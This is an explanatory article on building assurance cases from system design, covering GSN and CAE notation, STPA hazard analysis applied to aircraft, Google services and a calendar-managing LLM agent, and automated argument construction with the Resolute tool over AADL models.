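# Assurance from system design: claims, arguments and evidence for software and AI before deployment

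## What an assurance case is and what a design can contribute

An assurance case is a structured argument, supported by evidence, that a system has a stated property in a stated environment. Engineers call it a safety case or a security case when the property is safety or security. Developers usually prepare one before a system enters service, and a regulator, customer or independent assessor reads it to decide whether the system should enter service. Developers can produce some of the evidence before they build the system, because some properties follow from the design alone. How much evidence a design can provide depends on the property and on whether any of the system's parts learned their behaviour from data.

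A claim is a statement about the system that is either true or false. Claims can also cover the people who design it. Adelard's *Claims, Arguments and Evidence (CAE)*, a guide from a British safety consultancy, includes the example "Design personnel are suitably qualified". Evidence is the material at the bottom of the case, such as a proof, an analysis, a test result or a record. The argument is the reasoning that links a claim to the smaller claims or evidence beneath it. Context and assumptions limit what a claim means. Context sets the claim's scope, such as the system version and operating conditions it covers. An assumption is a statement that the case relies on but deliberately does not support.

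An assurance case must include an explicit argument, which older methods lack. *The Interpretation and Evaluation of Assurance Cases* (Rushby, 2015) compares assurance cases with DO-178C, the guidelines for software on commercial aircraft. DO-178C contains 71 objectives for the most critical software, but no explicit argument for why meeting them makes the software fit to fly.

### A small example

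In one example, a ground station steers a quadcopter by radio. The station encrypts its messages, and a component on the aircraft, Decrypt, rejects anything without the right encryption. The owner wants to know that a stranger's radio commands cannot reach the motors. Gacek, Backes and colleagues (2014) worked through this problem in *Resolute* for a research drone in a programme of DARPA, the US defence research agency. The tree below uses three of their claims; the context, assumption, strategy and evidence are illustrative additions. It follows Goal Structuring Notation (GSN), the most popular way of drawing such arguments.

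- Goal G1: The motor controller only receives messages from the ground station.
  - Context C1: Architecture model of the quadcopter
  - Strategy S1: Argument over who can get a message through Decrypt, and over what reaches the motor controller
    - Goal G2: Only the ground station can send messages that pass Decrypt.
      - Assumption A1: Nobody can break the cipher without the key.
      - Solution Sn1: Test report for Decrypt
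      - Solution Sn2: Key-handling records
    - Goal G3: The motor controller only receives messages that pass Decrypt.
      - Solution Sn3: Trace of every connection in the architecture model

GSN draws goals (claims) as rectangles, strategies (descriptions of the reasoning) as parallelograms and solutions (references to evidence) as circles. Arrows with solid heads point from a goal to whatever supports it, and arrows with hollow heads point to context and assumptions. The SCSC Assurance Case Working Group's *Goal Structuring Notation Community Standard* (2021) requires a goal to be a full sentence, because it must be something that can be true or false, and a solution to be a noun phrase, because it is not a claim. The standard also forbids loops, so no goal can support itself, even indirectly. An assumption applies to the whole argument below the point where it is attached.

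If G2 and G3 are both true, G1 must be true, so the step is deductive. Many steps in real cases are weaker. "We have dealt with every hazard on our list, so the system is safe" is a reasonable argument, but it fails if there is a hazard that nobody listed. Rushby calls such steps inductive and would like to remove them from the interior of a case, so that the only doubt is whether the evidence supports the lowest claims, but calls this proposal radical and leaves open whether it is feasible. The quadcopter tree already fits the proposal, and its doubts are easy to find. The tests of Decrypt may have missed some malformed message, or somebody may have copied the key. Drawing the tree does not remove these doubts, and the standard states explicitly that GSN only documents an argument and does not establish that it is true.

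The main rival to GSN is Claims-Arguments-Evidence (CAE), a notation developed by Adelard. CAE uses different shapes, and its arrows run the other way, from support up to claim. More importantly, CAE puts more weight on the written justification for each step, and GSN on the overall structure. GSN gives context and assumptions their own symbols, whereas Adelard puts explanations of terms and scope inside the claim itself. Sources disagree on how strict CAE is. According to Rushby, CAE requires an argument between a claim and its subclaims, while GSN allows a direct link. Adelard's own guide, however, treats the argument element as optional, though often good practice, and allows a direct link where the approach is straightforward or the audience already understands it. In either notation, omitting the argument risks two readers filling the gap with different reasoning without noticing.

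### Where safety cases came from

Safety cases began in the nuclear and chemical industries. Rushby recounts that Britain's nuclear industry started using them for plant design in the 1950s, after the Windscale accident of 1957, and that legislation made them compulsory in 1965. In 1972 a government committee under Lord Robens recommended that those who create a risk should be responsible for controlling it, and that regulations should set goals instead of prescribing methods. Two years later an accident at a chemical plant in Flixborough killed 28 people. British regulators drafted rules that would have required hazardous sites to produce something close to a safety case. After a large release of dioxin at Seveso in Italy, the European Community issued a similar directive.

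Offshore oil and gas stayed under an older permit system until 1988, when an explosion on the Piper Alpha platform killed 167 people. Lord Cullen's inquiry recommended safety cases for the offshore industry too. Within a decade of the switch to safety cases, reportable offshore accidents in the UK had fallen by more than 75%. A before-and-after comparison cannot show how much of that fall came from the safety cases, because other things also changed in those years.

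Computers later led engineers to add an explicit argument to safety cases. In the late 1970s Britain was considering an American reactor design that relied on computers for more of its functions, including the emergency shutdown. Safety cases at the time were long narratives about the design, and the engineers had no good way to fit a computer system into one, so they required an argument that explained how the evidence met the goals. Even then, the arguments were often hard to find in the prose. Three researchers who studied industrial safety cases in 1995 reported that they always had to annotate and cross-reference the text to extract the argument. GSN, from the University of York, and CAE both grew out of efforts in that period to make the argument's structure visible.

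The practice has since spread beyond nuclear power and oil. The US Food and Drug Administration requires a safety case for infusion pumps, which feed drugs into patients at a controlled rate, and Rushby cites a review of safety cases in aviation, cars, defence, petrochemicals, railways and medical devices. Civil aircraft software is a partial exception because it is still governed mainly by DO-178C, which mentions an assurance case as one way to justify departing from the usual methods.

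### Design, tests and records

Rushby describes the evidence in an assurance case as being about a system's design, development and tested behaviour. The quadcopter tree has one of each. The trace of connections (Sn3) is an analysis of the design, the key-handling records (Sn2) document how people did their work, and the test report (Sn1) comes from running a finished component.

Engineers can analyze a design before anyone writes the code, and the analysis can cover every case the design allows. But if the built system departs from the design, even a correct analysis may not apply to it.

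Testing, by contrast, runs the real program on the real hardware, including any mistakes that never appeared in a design document. But it can only sample the program's behavior, because even a program of moderate size has more possible paths than anyone can test. The confidence that a run of successful tests justifies has to be estimated statistically, and the results are sometimes discouraging.

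Development records are the most indirect kind of evidence. They show that qualified people reviewed the requirements or kept track of versions, which makes errors less likely but doesn't show that any particular error is absent. They are still useful. Rushby notes that modern airliners are extraordinarily safe and that nobody has traced a serious incident to software that failed to meet its requirements, although investigators have traced some to requirements that were themselves wrong. That is a good record for an approach that relies heavily on orderly process, but it is much less clear whether it carries over to systems unlike their predecessors.

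Real cases mix these sources. The GSN standard's sample argument, for an imaginary control system, cites formal verification (mathematical proof that a system meets its specification) to show that one hazard has been eliminated. It uses a fault tree (an analysis of how component failures combine) to show that another has a yearly probability below one in a million. For the software, it cites process evidence that the developers worked to the required level of rigour. None of the four items of evidence is itself a test report. The example shows how much a case can rely on other kinds of evidence, though it should not be read as a recommendation to skip testing. Bloomfield and Rushby (2025), in *AI Assurance Needs a Systems Engineering Approach*, argue that testing is not enough because engineers must also understand how the system works, how it can fail and why its critical properties hold.

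### What an architecture model contains

An architecture model is a machine-readable description of a system's components, their connections and the hardware they run on, so software can analyse it. One standard language for writing these models is AADL, the Architecture Analysis and Design Language, which engineers use for embedded systems such as those in aircraft. In SAE International's *Architecture Analysis & Design Language (AADL)* (2012), a model is a hierarchy of components with interfaces, interconnections and properties. Some components represent hardware, such as processors, memory and buses (the shared wiring that carries data between devices). Others represent software, such as processes and threads (single running sequences of instructions). The model also records the allocation of software to hardware, such as which processes share a memory.

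The architecture model treats each component as a black box. It specifies only what is needed for the component to interact with the others, and leaves out the code that implements it. Gacek and colleagues chose this deliberately, because an analysis that had to cover every line of code would not scale to a whole aircraft. Their full model of the drone's flight software had over 7,000 lines of AADL and 35 threads, while the implementation had more than 50,000 lines of C.

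The omission limits which claims a model can support. Component claims, such as that Decrypt rejects forged messages, need evidence from inside the component. A model is most useful for claims about how the components fit together, because the properties of a system do not follow simply from the properties of its parts. Rushby's example is that nobody could show an aeroplane to be safe by showing that its wheels, rudder and wings are each safe. One of the standard argument steps in CAE therefore splits a claim into subclaims that the architecture establishes, such as that a fault in one part cannot spread to another, and subclaims that the components establish. Some claims about the whole system need more than architecture. *ACCESS* (2024), a paper on building safety-critical systems around their assurance cases, accepts that architectural data are sufficient for security claims like the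 quadcopter's, but treats safety claims as needing further models, including models of the hazards.

### Structure and learned behaviour

Goal G3, that no message reaches the motor controller without passing through Decrypt, is a claim about structure. An engineer can settle it by tracing connections backwards through the model, which ends with an answer because there are finitely many connections. In the simplified quadcopter, the motor controller takes its commands from a navigation component. That component receives sensor readings, which are exempt from the claim, and messages from a command component, which gets its input from Decrypt. At each step, the engineer also has to establish that the connection delivers the data unaltered.

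Gacek and colleagues then ran the same check on a version of the model with a safety controller that could bypass Decrypt and send messages straight to the aircraft. The claim failed, and the failed argument pointed to the radio component feeding the navigation component. The check found the bypass without a flight test, which would have exposed it only if someone had thought to transmit on that channel.

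The answer holds for the model. If a programmer adds a connection in the code that isn't in the model, the trace cannot show it. For this reason, the AADL standard from SAE International includes rules for when a physical system conforms to its model.

Now suppose the quadcopter gets a camera and a neural network that chooses landing spots, and the claim is that the network never chooses a spot with a person on it. The design specifies the number of layers and the format of the input image and output coordinates. Two networks with exactly this design, trained on different pictures, can choose differently, so the design can't settle the claim. *A Structured Approach to Safety Case Construction for AI Systems* (Lee, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) describes the same problem at a larger scale. Classical safety cases depend on precise specifications and predictable components, whereas developers of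 modern AI systems discover after training what their systems can do. Engineers can sometimes prove a narrow property of a small network, but they do it by analysing the trained weights, which belong to the finished component and not to its design.

An architecture model treats ordinary software as a black box for convenience, and an engineer who needs more detail can read the code. A trained network is a black box in a different sense, because opening it yields millions of numbers. Bloomfield and Rushby conclude that learned components should count as untrusted, and that something outside them should check or guard what they do while the system runs. The design can show whether outputs must pass through that check. The claim "No landing spot reaches the flight controller without passing the obstacle check" has the same form as G3, and an engineer can settle it with the same kind of trace.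 The trace cannot show that the obstacle check works well, however, and Bloomfield and Rushby concede that a guard for perception may itself need AI.

In their combative position paper, they call the alignment of opaque models an intractable problem. Lee and colleagues still allow claims about the model itself, such as that it cannot perform some harmful task, with evaluations among the evidence. An assurance case can include both structural claims and claims about the model, but fewer structural claims are available when there is little conventional engineering around the model.

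Building a case from a design therefore raises three questions. The first is where the claims come from, which matters because a trace is useful only if somebody knew to ask about the motors. Hazard analysis methods such as STPA (System-Theoretic Process Analysis) address this. The second is how software can build the argument automatically from an architecture model, as Gacek and colleagues' tool Resolute does. The third is what testing must still add once the system exists.

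## Turning hazards into claims

Hazard analysis looks for questions to ask about a design, such as whether a stranger's commands can reach the quadcopter's motors. STPA looks for these questions by examining how the parts of a system control one another. The *STPA Handbook* (Leveson and Thomas, 2018) recommends starting while the system is still an early concept, so that the results can shape the design. Each result is linked to the harm it concerns, which makes it easy to reuse in an assurance case.

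The method assumes that accidents can happen even when every part works as specified. The Mars Polar Lander, for example, crashed although no part had broken. It needed its descent engines until it touched the ground, which sensors in its legs were meant to detect. Unfolding the legs also triggered the sensors, but the software requirements didn't mention this, so the software treated the signal as a landing and shut the engines down 40 metres above the surface. Thomas (2024) sets out this kind of crash as a chain: a false touchdown signal, a wrong entry in the computer's model of the situation, a command to disable the thrusters, and a lost spacecraft.

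### Losses, hazards and constraints

An analysis starts with a list of losses, which are outcomes that some stakeholder finds unacceptable, such as deaths, injuries or a leak of sensitive information. The analyst then looks for hazards, which are system states that lead to a loss under some worst-case conditions of the environment. Separating the two keeps attention on what designers can control. The designers of a nuclear plant can't control the wind direction, but they can design against a release of radioactive material, so the release is the hazard.

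Under Leveson and Thomas's rules for wording hazards, a hazard describes the whole system, so "brake failure" is a possible cause of a hazard, not a hazard. It also has to be a state that nobody ever wants, which rules out "aircraft in flight", even though some accidents can only happen in flight. The description shouldn't include the word "unsafe", because the hazard is supposed to define what unsafe means.

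Inverting a hazard gives a constraint. The hazard "Aircraft violate minimum separation standards" becomes the constraint "Aircraft must satisfy minimum separation standards". A constraint can also apply when prevention fails. For example, if two aircraft get too close, something must detect it and keep them from colliding.

A constraint is an instruction, so developers must reword it as a claim, a statement that can be true or false, before using it in an assurance case. "Aircraft must satisfy minimum separation standards" becomes "Aircraft satisfy minimum separation standards", with context that specifies the airspace and equipment. The developers must then provide evidence that the claim is true.

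### The control structure

The analyst next draws the system as a hierarchy of control loops. In each loop, a controller sends control actions, or commands, to a process and receives feedback about it. The controller may be a program, a person or an organisation. It chooses commands using a process model, its internal picture of the process.

The handbook's main example is the wheel brakes of an aircraft. A brake computer has to apply the brakes automatically on landing, so it must register that the aircraft has landed. It needs feedback to do this, perhaps from switches that detect weight on the wheels. Analysts who work from responsibility to process model to feedback can notice, before anyone has chosen a sensor, that a controller lacks information it needs.

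An arrow in a control structure shows that one party can send information to another. The parties include people, such as pilots and air traffic controllers. Although the diagram looks a little like an architecture model, its arrows don't show the wire or radio link that carries the information. The recipient may not obey an instruction, so the analyst has to consider what happens if, for example, a pilot disregards one.

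### Unsafe control actions and loss scenarios

The analyst asks how each control action could lead to a hazard. A control action can do so in four ways, which the table illustrates with the automatic brakes.

| How the action is unsafe | Example | Constraint on the brake computer |
|---|---|---|
| Not given | No brake command during the landing roll, although the crew has armed the system | Command braking during the landing roll when armed |
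| Given wrongly | Brake command during a normal takeoff | Do not command braking during a normal takeoff |
| Wrong time or order | Brake command too long after touchdown | Command braking within a set time of touchdown |
| Wrong duration | Braking stops before the aircraft has slowed to taxi speed | Keep braking until taxi speed |

The context matters because braking is unsafe only in some situations. "Given wrongly" also covers a command with the wrong strength or direction, such as too little braking or braking on one side only. Analysts list an unsafe action even when the design includes a backup, since the backup may fail too. They invert each entry into a constraint, as they do with hazards, but the resulting claim is narrower and covers a single controller.

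The last step is to write loss scenarios, which explain how each unsafe action could come about. In one scenario, an aircraft lands on a wet runway and its wheels skim over the water without spinning up, so the brake computer still registers the aircraft as airborne and never brakes. Leveson and Thomas describe a similar accident involving thrust reversers, which slow an aircraft after landing. An airliner's software kept them locked on a wet runway, so the airliner ran off the end into a small hill.

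Scenarios also cover correct commands that have no effect, for instance because hydraulic pressure is too low. The scenario largely determines what evidence the developers need. For the wet runway, they need to analyze how the software is designed to detect a landing, while for low pressure they need evidence about pumps and leaks.

### A calendar agent from start to finish

In *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents*, Doshi, Hong and colleagues (2026) adapt STPA to AI agents, meaning language models that can call software tools. Their example agent resolves clashes in a user's calendar using three tools: `list_events` reads the calendar, `update_event` changes an event and `send_email` sends a message. They chose a narrow agent because it is hard to write precise safety requirements for an agent that might do anything.

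In the scenario, a user adds an appointment for treatment of a sexually transmitted disease. The appointment clashes with a work meeting with Bob, a colleague. The agent offers to move the meeting to 3 pm, the user agrees, and the agent's notification email reveals the appointment to colleagues. There is no attacker, and all three tools work properly.

The adapted method starts with the people the agent affects. The user values privacy, so one loss is a leak of private information. The other attendees value timely communication, so another loss is late notice of a change. Doshi and colleagues go straight from these losses to the behaviours that could cause them, without drawing a control structure or sorting commands into the four types. The behaviours still fit the types easily enough, since an email containing private details is a command given wrongly, and failing to email attendees about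 a moved meeting is a command not given.

Two requirements follow. The agent must include only essential event details in notification emails and leave out private information, such as a personal reason for the change, unless the user explicitly authorises sharing it. It must also promptly notify all other attendees whenever it updates an event.

A language model might interpret such sentences in many ways, and no program can check them as they stand. Doshi and colleagues therefore turn each one into a formal specification:

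- **SPEC1** treats the details of every event as private to people who aren't attending it. Anything derived from private information is at least as private, although users may confirm the privacy labels themselves. No `send_email` call may include data that is private to the recipient.
- **SPEC2** requires one `send_email` to every attendee directly after each `update_event`.

SPEC1 is an example of information flow control, which labels data by secrecy or trust and blocks movements that the labels forbid. Bob may learn the new time of his own meeting, but not why it moved, because he isn't attending the medical appointment. SPEC2 is a rule about the order of events. It is weaker than the original requirement to notify people of the change, because a blank email to everyone would satisfy SPEC2 as worded. If the assurance case claims that attendees learn of changes, evidence for SPEC2 supports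 only part of the claim.

The next decision is how strictly to enforce each rule. Doshi and colleagues use four tiers, which apply both to movements of data and to sequences of tool calls:

- **Blocklist:** the system always refuses these, such as private data going into `send_email`.
- **Mustlist:** the system requires these, such as an email to each attendee after an update.
- **Allowlist:** these go ahead without asking the user, such as the first notification to each attendee.
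- **Confirmation:** the user must approve these, such as an email that includes private information.

The tiers are a compromise between safety and usefulness. Asking the user about everything would be simple, but people stop paying attention to prompts when they see too many. Forbidding `send_email` after any use of `list_events` would stop anything from the calendar getting out, but it would also seem to block the emails that SPEC2 requires, since the agent presumably has to read the calendar to find a clash. A less restrictive option is to hide unrelated events from the model before it writes the message.

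Enforcement has to happen outside the language model, in a component that intercepts each tool call and checks it before it runs. This component needs reliable labels on data and tools. Doshi and colleagues propose adding mandatory labels to the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting models to tools. The labels would record how confidential the data is, whether its source is trustworthy and what the tool can do. A company can probably trust the labels on its own tools, but tools from an open market would need some form of certification.

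To test the idea, they modelled the system in Alloy, a language for describing designs in formal logic. The model contains the tools, the messages and the steps of execution, with labels for confidentiality and integrity. They wrote each hazard as a condition, such as `private_leak`, which is true if private data reaches an unauthorised tool. Alloy's analyser then searches every sequence of steps up to a fixed length for one that makes the condition true.

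The analyser quickly found counterexamples without the policies, such as private data ending up in an external email, but found none with them. It also confirmed that useful sequences of tool calls remained possible, including creating an event, rescheduling it and emailing the participants without a leak. This second check matters because a policy that blocked every tool call would also prevent leaks.

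The check covers bounded traces of a model, not a running agent. The resulting claim would be roughly that, in the modelled design, no sequence of steps within the bound sends private data to an unauthorised tool. The search could miss a leak that needs a longer sequence or depends on a wrong label. The policy engine that would intercept real tool calls was still future work. Even so, the result doesn't depend on a language model recognising that a medical appointment is sensitive, but a filter that asks another language model to review outgoing emails would depend on that.

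### From the chain to a tree of claims

STPA produces a chain from losses through hazards, control actions and unsafe control actions to scenarios and their remedies. *A system-theoretic assurance framework for safety-driven systems engineering* (Ahlbrecht, Sprockhoff and Durak, 2024) turns this chain into a GSN argument with one level of goals for each link, and demonstrates it on a system that alerts pilots to other aircraft. The table follows one branch of that argument, with the claims reworded for readability.

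| Level | Result from STPA | Claim |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Loss: an aircraft, in a collision | The system is free of unacceptable risks leading to losses |
| 2 | Hazard: aircraft come too close | The design mitigates the hazards |
| 3 | Control action: a warning to the pilot | The system does not issue or withhold warnings unsafely |
| 4 | Unsafe control action: no warning on a collision course | This action does not occur in operation |
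| 5 | Scenario: the pilot has selected the wrong mode | The design prevents this scenario |
| 6 | Remedy: feedback to the pilot about the current mode | Developers have implemented and verified the feedback |

Because the model already contains every link, an ordinary script can build the tree. It creates the top two levels and then works down through each control action, unsafe action, scenario and remedy. If one remedy deals with several scenarios, the script links to the existing goal instead of copying it. Building the tree doesn't require a language model, though one can help with the analysis itself, as in *An LLM-Integrated Framework for Completion, Management, and Tracing of STPA* (2025).

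The bottom level is the most demanding because it requires a remedy that developers have both implemented and verified. If the calendar agent had such a tree, the Alloy result would support the claim that, in the design, the email policy prevents the leak. The bottom goal would stay open until somebody had built the policy engine and shown that it enforces the policy.

Breaking hazards down this far also helps make safety arguments more concrete. Gleirscher and Carlan (2017) observed in *Arguing from Hazard Analysis in Safety Cases* that these arguments tend to stay too abstract, with evidence nodes that refer to large packages of documents. A reviewer can check a claim like "the display shows the pilot the current mode" much more easily than a reference like "see hazard analysis".

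Each level also depends on assumptions. At the top, the argument assumes that the analysts found every relevant loss, and lower down it assumes that they found every unsafe action and scenario. A GSN argument normally leaves its assumptions unsupported, but Ahlbrecht and colleagues tie each one to an activity that should justify it, such as peer review. The software flags activities that nobody has carried out and unsafe actions with no scenarios listed. In their deliberately unfinished example, they had accepted the planned activities for 12 assumptions as adequate but had carried out only eight of them.

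*Systematic Hazard Analysis for Frontier AI using STPA* (Mylius, 2025) proposes building safety cases for frontier AI from STPA results in a similar way.

### Google's experience

Google has used STPA on large software systems, where the usual loss is an outage. According to the company's own 2021 paper on its pilot, cited by Mylius, two engineers working part-time for five months found defects, and finding them earlier would probably have prevented at least four major incidents. That is a good result for the effort, but the estimate is retrospective and doesn't show what the same engineers would have found with another method.

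*The Evolution of SRE at Google* (Falzone and Treynor Sloss, 2024) gives a worked example. Google sets quotas on the computing resources that some internal services may use, and a program called the quota rightsizer automatically lowers the quota of a service that consistently uses less. This control action, reducing a quota, is unsafe if it takes the quota below what the service needs, so the requirement is that the rightsizer must never do that.

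The engineers then looked for scenarios that would break the requirement. They had already examined the algorithm that adjusts quotas closely, but had given less attention to the complicated calculation of how much a service is using, which the algorithm relies on. If that figure were too low, the rightsizer would leave the service with too few resources even while working exactly as designed.

In 2021 this happened to a critical service. The rightsizer received a wrong usage figure and calculated a quota far below what the service was using. The system held the change for several weeks so that somebody could intervene, but it never notified anyone. When the reduction took effect, it caused a significant outage. Falzone and Treynor Sloss don't make clear whether the rightsizer was analyzed before or after the outage, so the case is better evidence that STPA can explain such an accident than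 that it can predict one.

They also report that later analyses, each taking engineer-weeks of work, have found hundreds of scenarios in some of Google's most complex systems before those scenarios led to an outage. This is the company's own account, and it doesn't include the number of outages that the analyses missed. *STPA Hazard Analysis Practice* (Thomas, Klein and Holthaus, 2026) shows that Google started training staff in STPA in 2021 with a class of 40, and that its engineers were still teaching it with John Thomas of MIT at a workshop in March 2026. The US Federal Aviation Administration also sponsored a joint effort by civil aviation authorities to learn and evaluate STPA.

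### Failure analysis and threat modelling

In failure modes and effects analysis (FMEA), analysts take a system's components one at a time and ask how each could fail and what would follow. This works well for a pump or a valve, but it is much less helpful when a system causes harm without any component failing. Leveson and Thomas describe rental cars with an anti-theft device that disabled the car if it moved with the engine off. When the cars were carried on a ferry, the devices disabled them as designed, and the ferry service stopped until enough tow trucks arrived. An FMEA of the calendar agent would probably miss the leaked appointment because no component failed there either.

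FMEA and related methods are better suited than STPA to numerical claims. Engineers can often estimate how frequently a valve sticks and combine such estimates into a probability for the system. STPA is qualitative, so it can't by itself support a claim that a hazard's yearly probability is below one in a million. The methods also combine well. If an STPA scenario involves a failed component, Ahlbrecht and colleagues suggest that the remedy can include an FMEA of that component.

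Leveson and Thomas make a stronger case for STPA, reporting that in every comparison it found all the scenarios that older methods found, plus many more, at much lower cost. Independent comparisons would carry more weight, because Leveson developed the theory behind STPA and their handbook refers readers to STPA workshop presentations for details.

In threat modelling, a common security method, analysts usually start with an adversary and work out what they want and how they could get it. STPA starts with the loss and treats an adversary as one more possible cause. For each scenario, the analyst asks whether somebody could cause it deliberately, for instance by faking the wheel-speed signal or blocking the brake command. An analysis limited to attackers would miss the leaked appointment. Doshi and colleagues similarly complain that most research on information flow in agents concentrates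 on attacks that hide instructions in the data an agent reads.

However, asking one extra question per scenario does little to account for a determined attacker, who may combine several weaknesses and adapt to the defences. Threat modelling can fill some of that gap, and Mylius suggests using it to generate the list of hazards for STPA.

### How complete is the result?

Leveson and Thomas call the four types of unsafe control action "provably complete". The claim is plausible, since a controller either gives a command or doesn't, and a command it gives can be wrong in its content, timing or duration. But the claim covers only the types, so analysts still have to identify the contexts in which a command is dangerous and the scenarios that could lead to it. *STPA Step 4 Building Scenarios* (Thomas, 2025) presents a more formal way of writing scenarios, partly so that reviewers can check them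 for gaps.

The guarantee also applies only to control actions in the control structure. If a controller is missing from that structure, the analysis has no row for its commands and the assurance case has no claim about them. For example, if the analyst had left out the quadcopter's safety controller, which could bypass Decrypt, the finished tree would still have looked complete, because the program that builds the tree can only flag gaps in what somebody entered.

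STPA has a good chance of finding that a design lacks feedback a controller needs, provided that the model includes the controller and its responsibilities. For example, an analyst who had assigned someone to review pending quota cuts would have had to ask how that person would learn about them. But if the model omits a feedback path that exists in the real system, nobody will ask what happens when that path carries a wrong value.

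The calendar agent shows how easily an analyst can miss a path. SPEC1 restricts what goes into `send_email`. Suppose the agent uses `update_event` to explain the new time, writing "moved because of medical appointment" in the description of the work meeting. Bob can read this in the shared calendar, so the appointment leaks even if every claim about email is true. An analyst who had drawn an arrow from the calendar to the other attendees would probably have noticed this and added a claim to the case about what `update_event` may write.

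Mislabelling an arrow in the control structure is less serious than omitting it. If an analyst records a command as feedback, the search for unsafe control actions will skip it, but Leveson and Thomas point out that the search for scenarios should find the same problem when it considers missing or delayed feedback. That later search doesn't provide the same check for an omitted arrow. Analysts can partly guard against omissions by comparing the control structure with an architecture model and asking about any connection missing from the control structure.

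## Computing an argument from an architecture model

When a claim is about how a system's parts fit together, software can often build the argument for it from the architecture model. Resolute, which Gacek and colleagues developed for DARPA's research drone, does this for models written in AADL. Engineers write general rules for justifying each kind of claim, and Resolute applies them to the components and connections in the model. If it finds a proof, that proof becomes the assurance case.

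The script that turns STPA results into a tree only arranges links that analysts have already entered. Resolute searches for its argument, and the search can fail, which means the design or the rules need work. Engineers can repeat the search after every design change, whereas a hand-drawn case easily falls out of date because it doesn't update when somebody adds a connection to the model.

A model is particularly useful for checking what surrounds a security mechanism. According to *Using AADL to Assess Architectural Concerns for Cyber Security* (2023), certification requires evidence that such a mechanism is correct, that nothing can bypass it and that it resists tampering. The last two depend on the rest of the system, which determines whether a message can bypass the quadcopter's Decrypt component or another program can alter the component's memory.

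### Claims and rules

In Resolute, a claim is a predicate, a statement with blanks for elements of the model. For example, `memory_protected(p)` means that no other process can alter the memory of process p. Each claim comes with an English sentence for readers of the finished case. Each rule gives a condition sufficient to establish a claim. A rule with blanks resembles an argument pattern, except that Resolute can fill in the blanks automatically.

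Gacek and colleagues give two rules for memory protection. In simplified notation, they are:

```
protected(p)  if  the operating system of p is seL4

protected(p)  if  for every memory m that holds p,
                  for every process q that m holds:
                  memory_safe(q)
```

The operating-system rule relies on seL4, a small kernel with formal proofs of its security properties. Resolute looks up p's operating system in the model, and the claim holds if the entry is "seL4".

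The shared-memory rule covers other operating systems. It relies on a further claim, that a process is memory safe, which roughly means that it can't write where it shouldn't. If Decrypt shares a memory chip with a camera program and a logging program, Resolute creates one subclaim for each of the three processes, and all three must hold. If the camera program isn't memory safe, this rule fails, but Decrypt's memory may still be protected under the operating-system rule, because only one rule has to succeed.

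Memory protection matters even when every message goes through Decrypt, as an attack staged in April 2017 showed. Rockwell Collins' *Secure Mathematically-Assured Composition of Control Models* (2017), the final report on the drone project, describes how the attackers broke into the quadcopter's camera software over Wi-Fi. On an insecure version of the aircraft, they could reach memory outside the camera's virtual machine, a simulated computer meant to confine the software. They replaced the encryption keys with their own, which changed the messages Decrypt would accept, so they did not need to bypass it. They then took control and landed the quadcopter in "hostile territory". When they tried the same attack on the secure version, which ran seL4, the attackers found only blank memory.

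### Computations and the ban on negation

Resolute keeps claims separate from computations, which calculate values from the model. One computation checks whether a process is assigned to a particular memory in the model. Another, from Gacek and colleagues, adds up the message delays of all the threads in a process. A computation can also run an outside analysis tool, such as one that checks whether every task will finish on time. Resolute runs the tool again whenever a rule needs the result.

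A computation produces a number rather than a claim, so an engineer has to put it inside a claim, such as "the message delay for p is within acceptable bounds", before it can appear in the assurance case.

Rules may negate a computation, but not a claim. A computation has a definite answer, because the model either places a process in a given memory or doesn't. The rules for a claim give only sufficient conditions for it. If both memory-protection rules fail, something no rule covers may still protect the process.

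Negating claims can be dangerous. Suppose the only rule for the claim `compromised(x)` checks for a software version known to be infected, and another engineer then writes a rule that x is trustworthy if it is not compromised. Every component with an unfamiliar infection would now count as trustworthy. Some logic programming languages do work this way, under a closed-world assumption that anything the program can't prove is false.

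Resolute makes no such assumption. To make a negative statement, an engineer must define it as a positive claim with its own rules. For example, `memory_violated` could have a rule that succeeds only if it finds a specific violation. Resolute also doesn't allow claims inside computations, since a computation could otherwise return "true" because a proof had failed.

### How the search works

Engineers usually keep their rules in a library, without asserting that they hold for any particular system. To start a search, they add a `prove` statement to a component in the model. The statement contains a claim and the elements it applies to, such as the claim about ground-station messages, applied to the motor controller.

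Logicians write Γ ⊢ G to mean that a goal G follows from a set of assumptions Γ. At the start of the search, Γ contains all the rules and G is the claim in the `prove` statement. Resolute then works backwards from G, and what it does next depends on the form of the goal:

- **A claim:** find a rule for it and try to prove the rule's condition.
- **"A and B", "A or B":** prove both parts, or prove either one.
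- **"If A, then B":** assume A and prove B. If A is a computation that comes out false, there is nothing left to prove.
- **"For every x":** list all the elements that x could be and prove the goal for each.
- **"For some x":** prove the goal for one element on the list.
- **A computation:** run it, and succeed if the answer is "true".

If every branch succeeds, Resolute turns the proof into an assurance case that an engineer can browse, replacing each claim with its English sentence and using the names of the actual components.

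Resolute allows "for every" only over finite sets because it proves the claim for each element separately. To prove ∀x G(x) over the elements t₁, …, tₙ, the program proves G(t₁), then G(t₂), and so on up to G(tₙ). This works for connections, threads and processes because a model contains a limited number of each, but the moments of a flight can't be listed in this way. Rockwell Collins therefore mainly used Resolute for claims about structure, such as which paths information can take, and had a separate tool for behaviour over time.

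Engineers can write computations that call themselves, however, and a badly written one may run forever even when the lists it searches are finite.

### A worked example

The quadcopter's owner wants to show that the motor controller only receives messages that pass Decrypt. Gacek and colleagues use two rules that refer to each other, one for components and one for connections. In simplified notation:

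```
clean(x)       if  for every connection c into x:
                   c carries sensor data, or clean_link(c)

clean_link(c)  if  c delivers data unaltered, and
                   its source is Decrypt or clean(source of c)
```

The table contains a small model based on theirs, with some details added for illustration. The handset is a hand-held radio controller. In this version of the design, the aircraft has a receiver for it, but the receiver isn't connected to anything else on board.

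| Connection | From | To | Sensor data? | Unaltered? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| c1 | Ground radio | Decrypt | No | No |
| c2 | Decrypt | Command | No | Yes |
| c3 | Command | Navigation | No | Yes |
| c4 | Sensors | Navigation | Yes | Yes |
| c5 | Navigation | Motor controller | No | Yes |
| c6 | Handset | Handset receiver | No | No |

The goal is clean(Motor controller), and the proof takes five steps:

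1. The only connection into the motor controller is c5. It doesn't carry sensor data, so Resolute must prove clean_link(c5).
2. c5 delivers data unaltered, but it comes from Navigation, not from Decrypt. The next goal is clean(Navigation).
3. Two connections lead into Navigation. c4 carries sensor data, which the rule allows. That leaves clean_link(c3).
4. c3 delivers data unaltered and comes from Command, so the next goal is clean(Command).
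5. The only connection into Command is c2, which delivers data unaltered and comes from Decrypt. The proof is complete.

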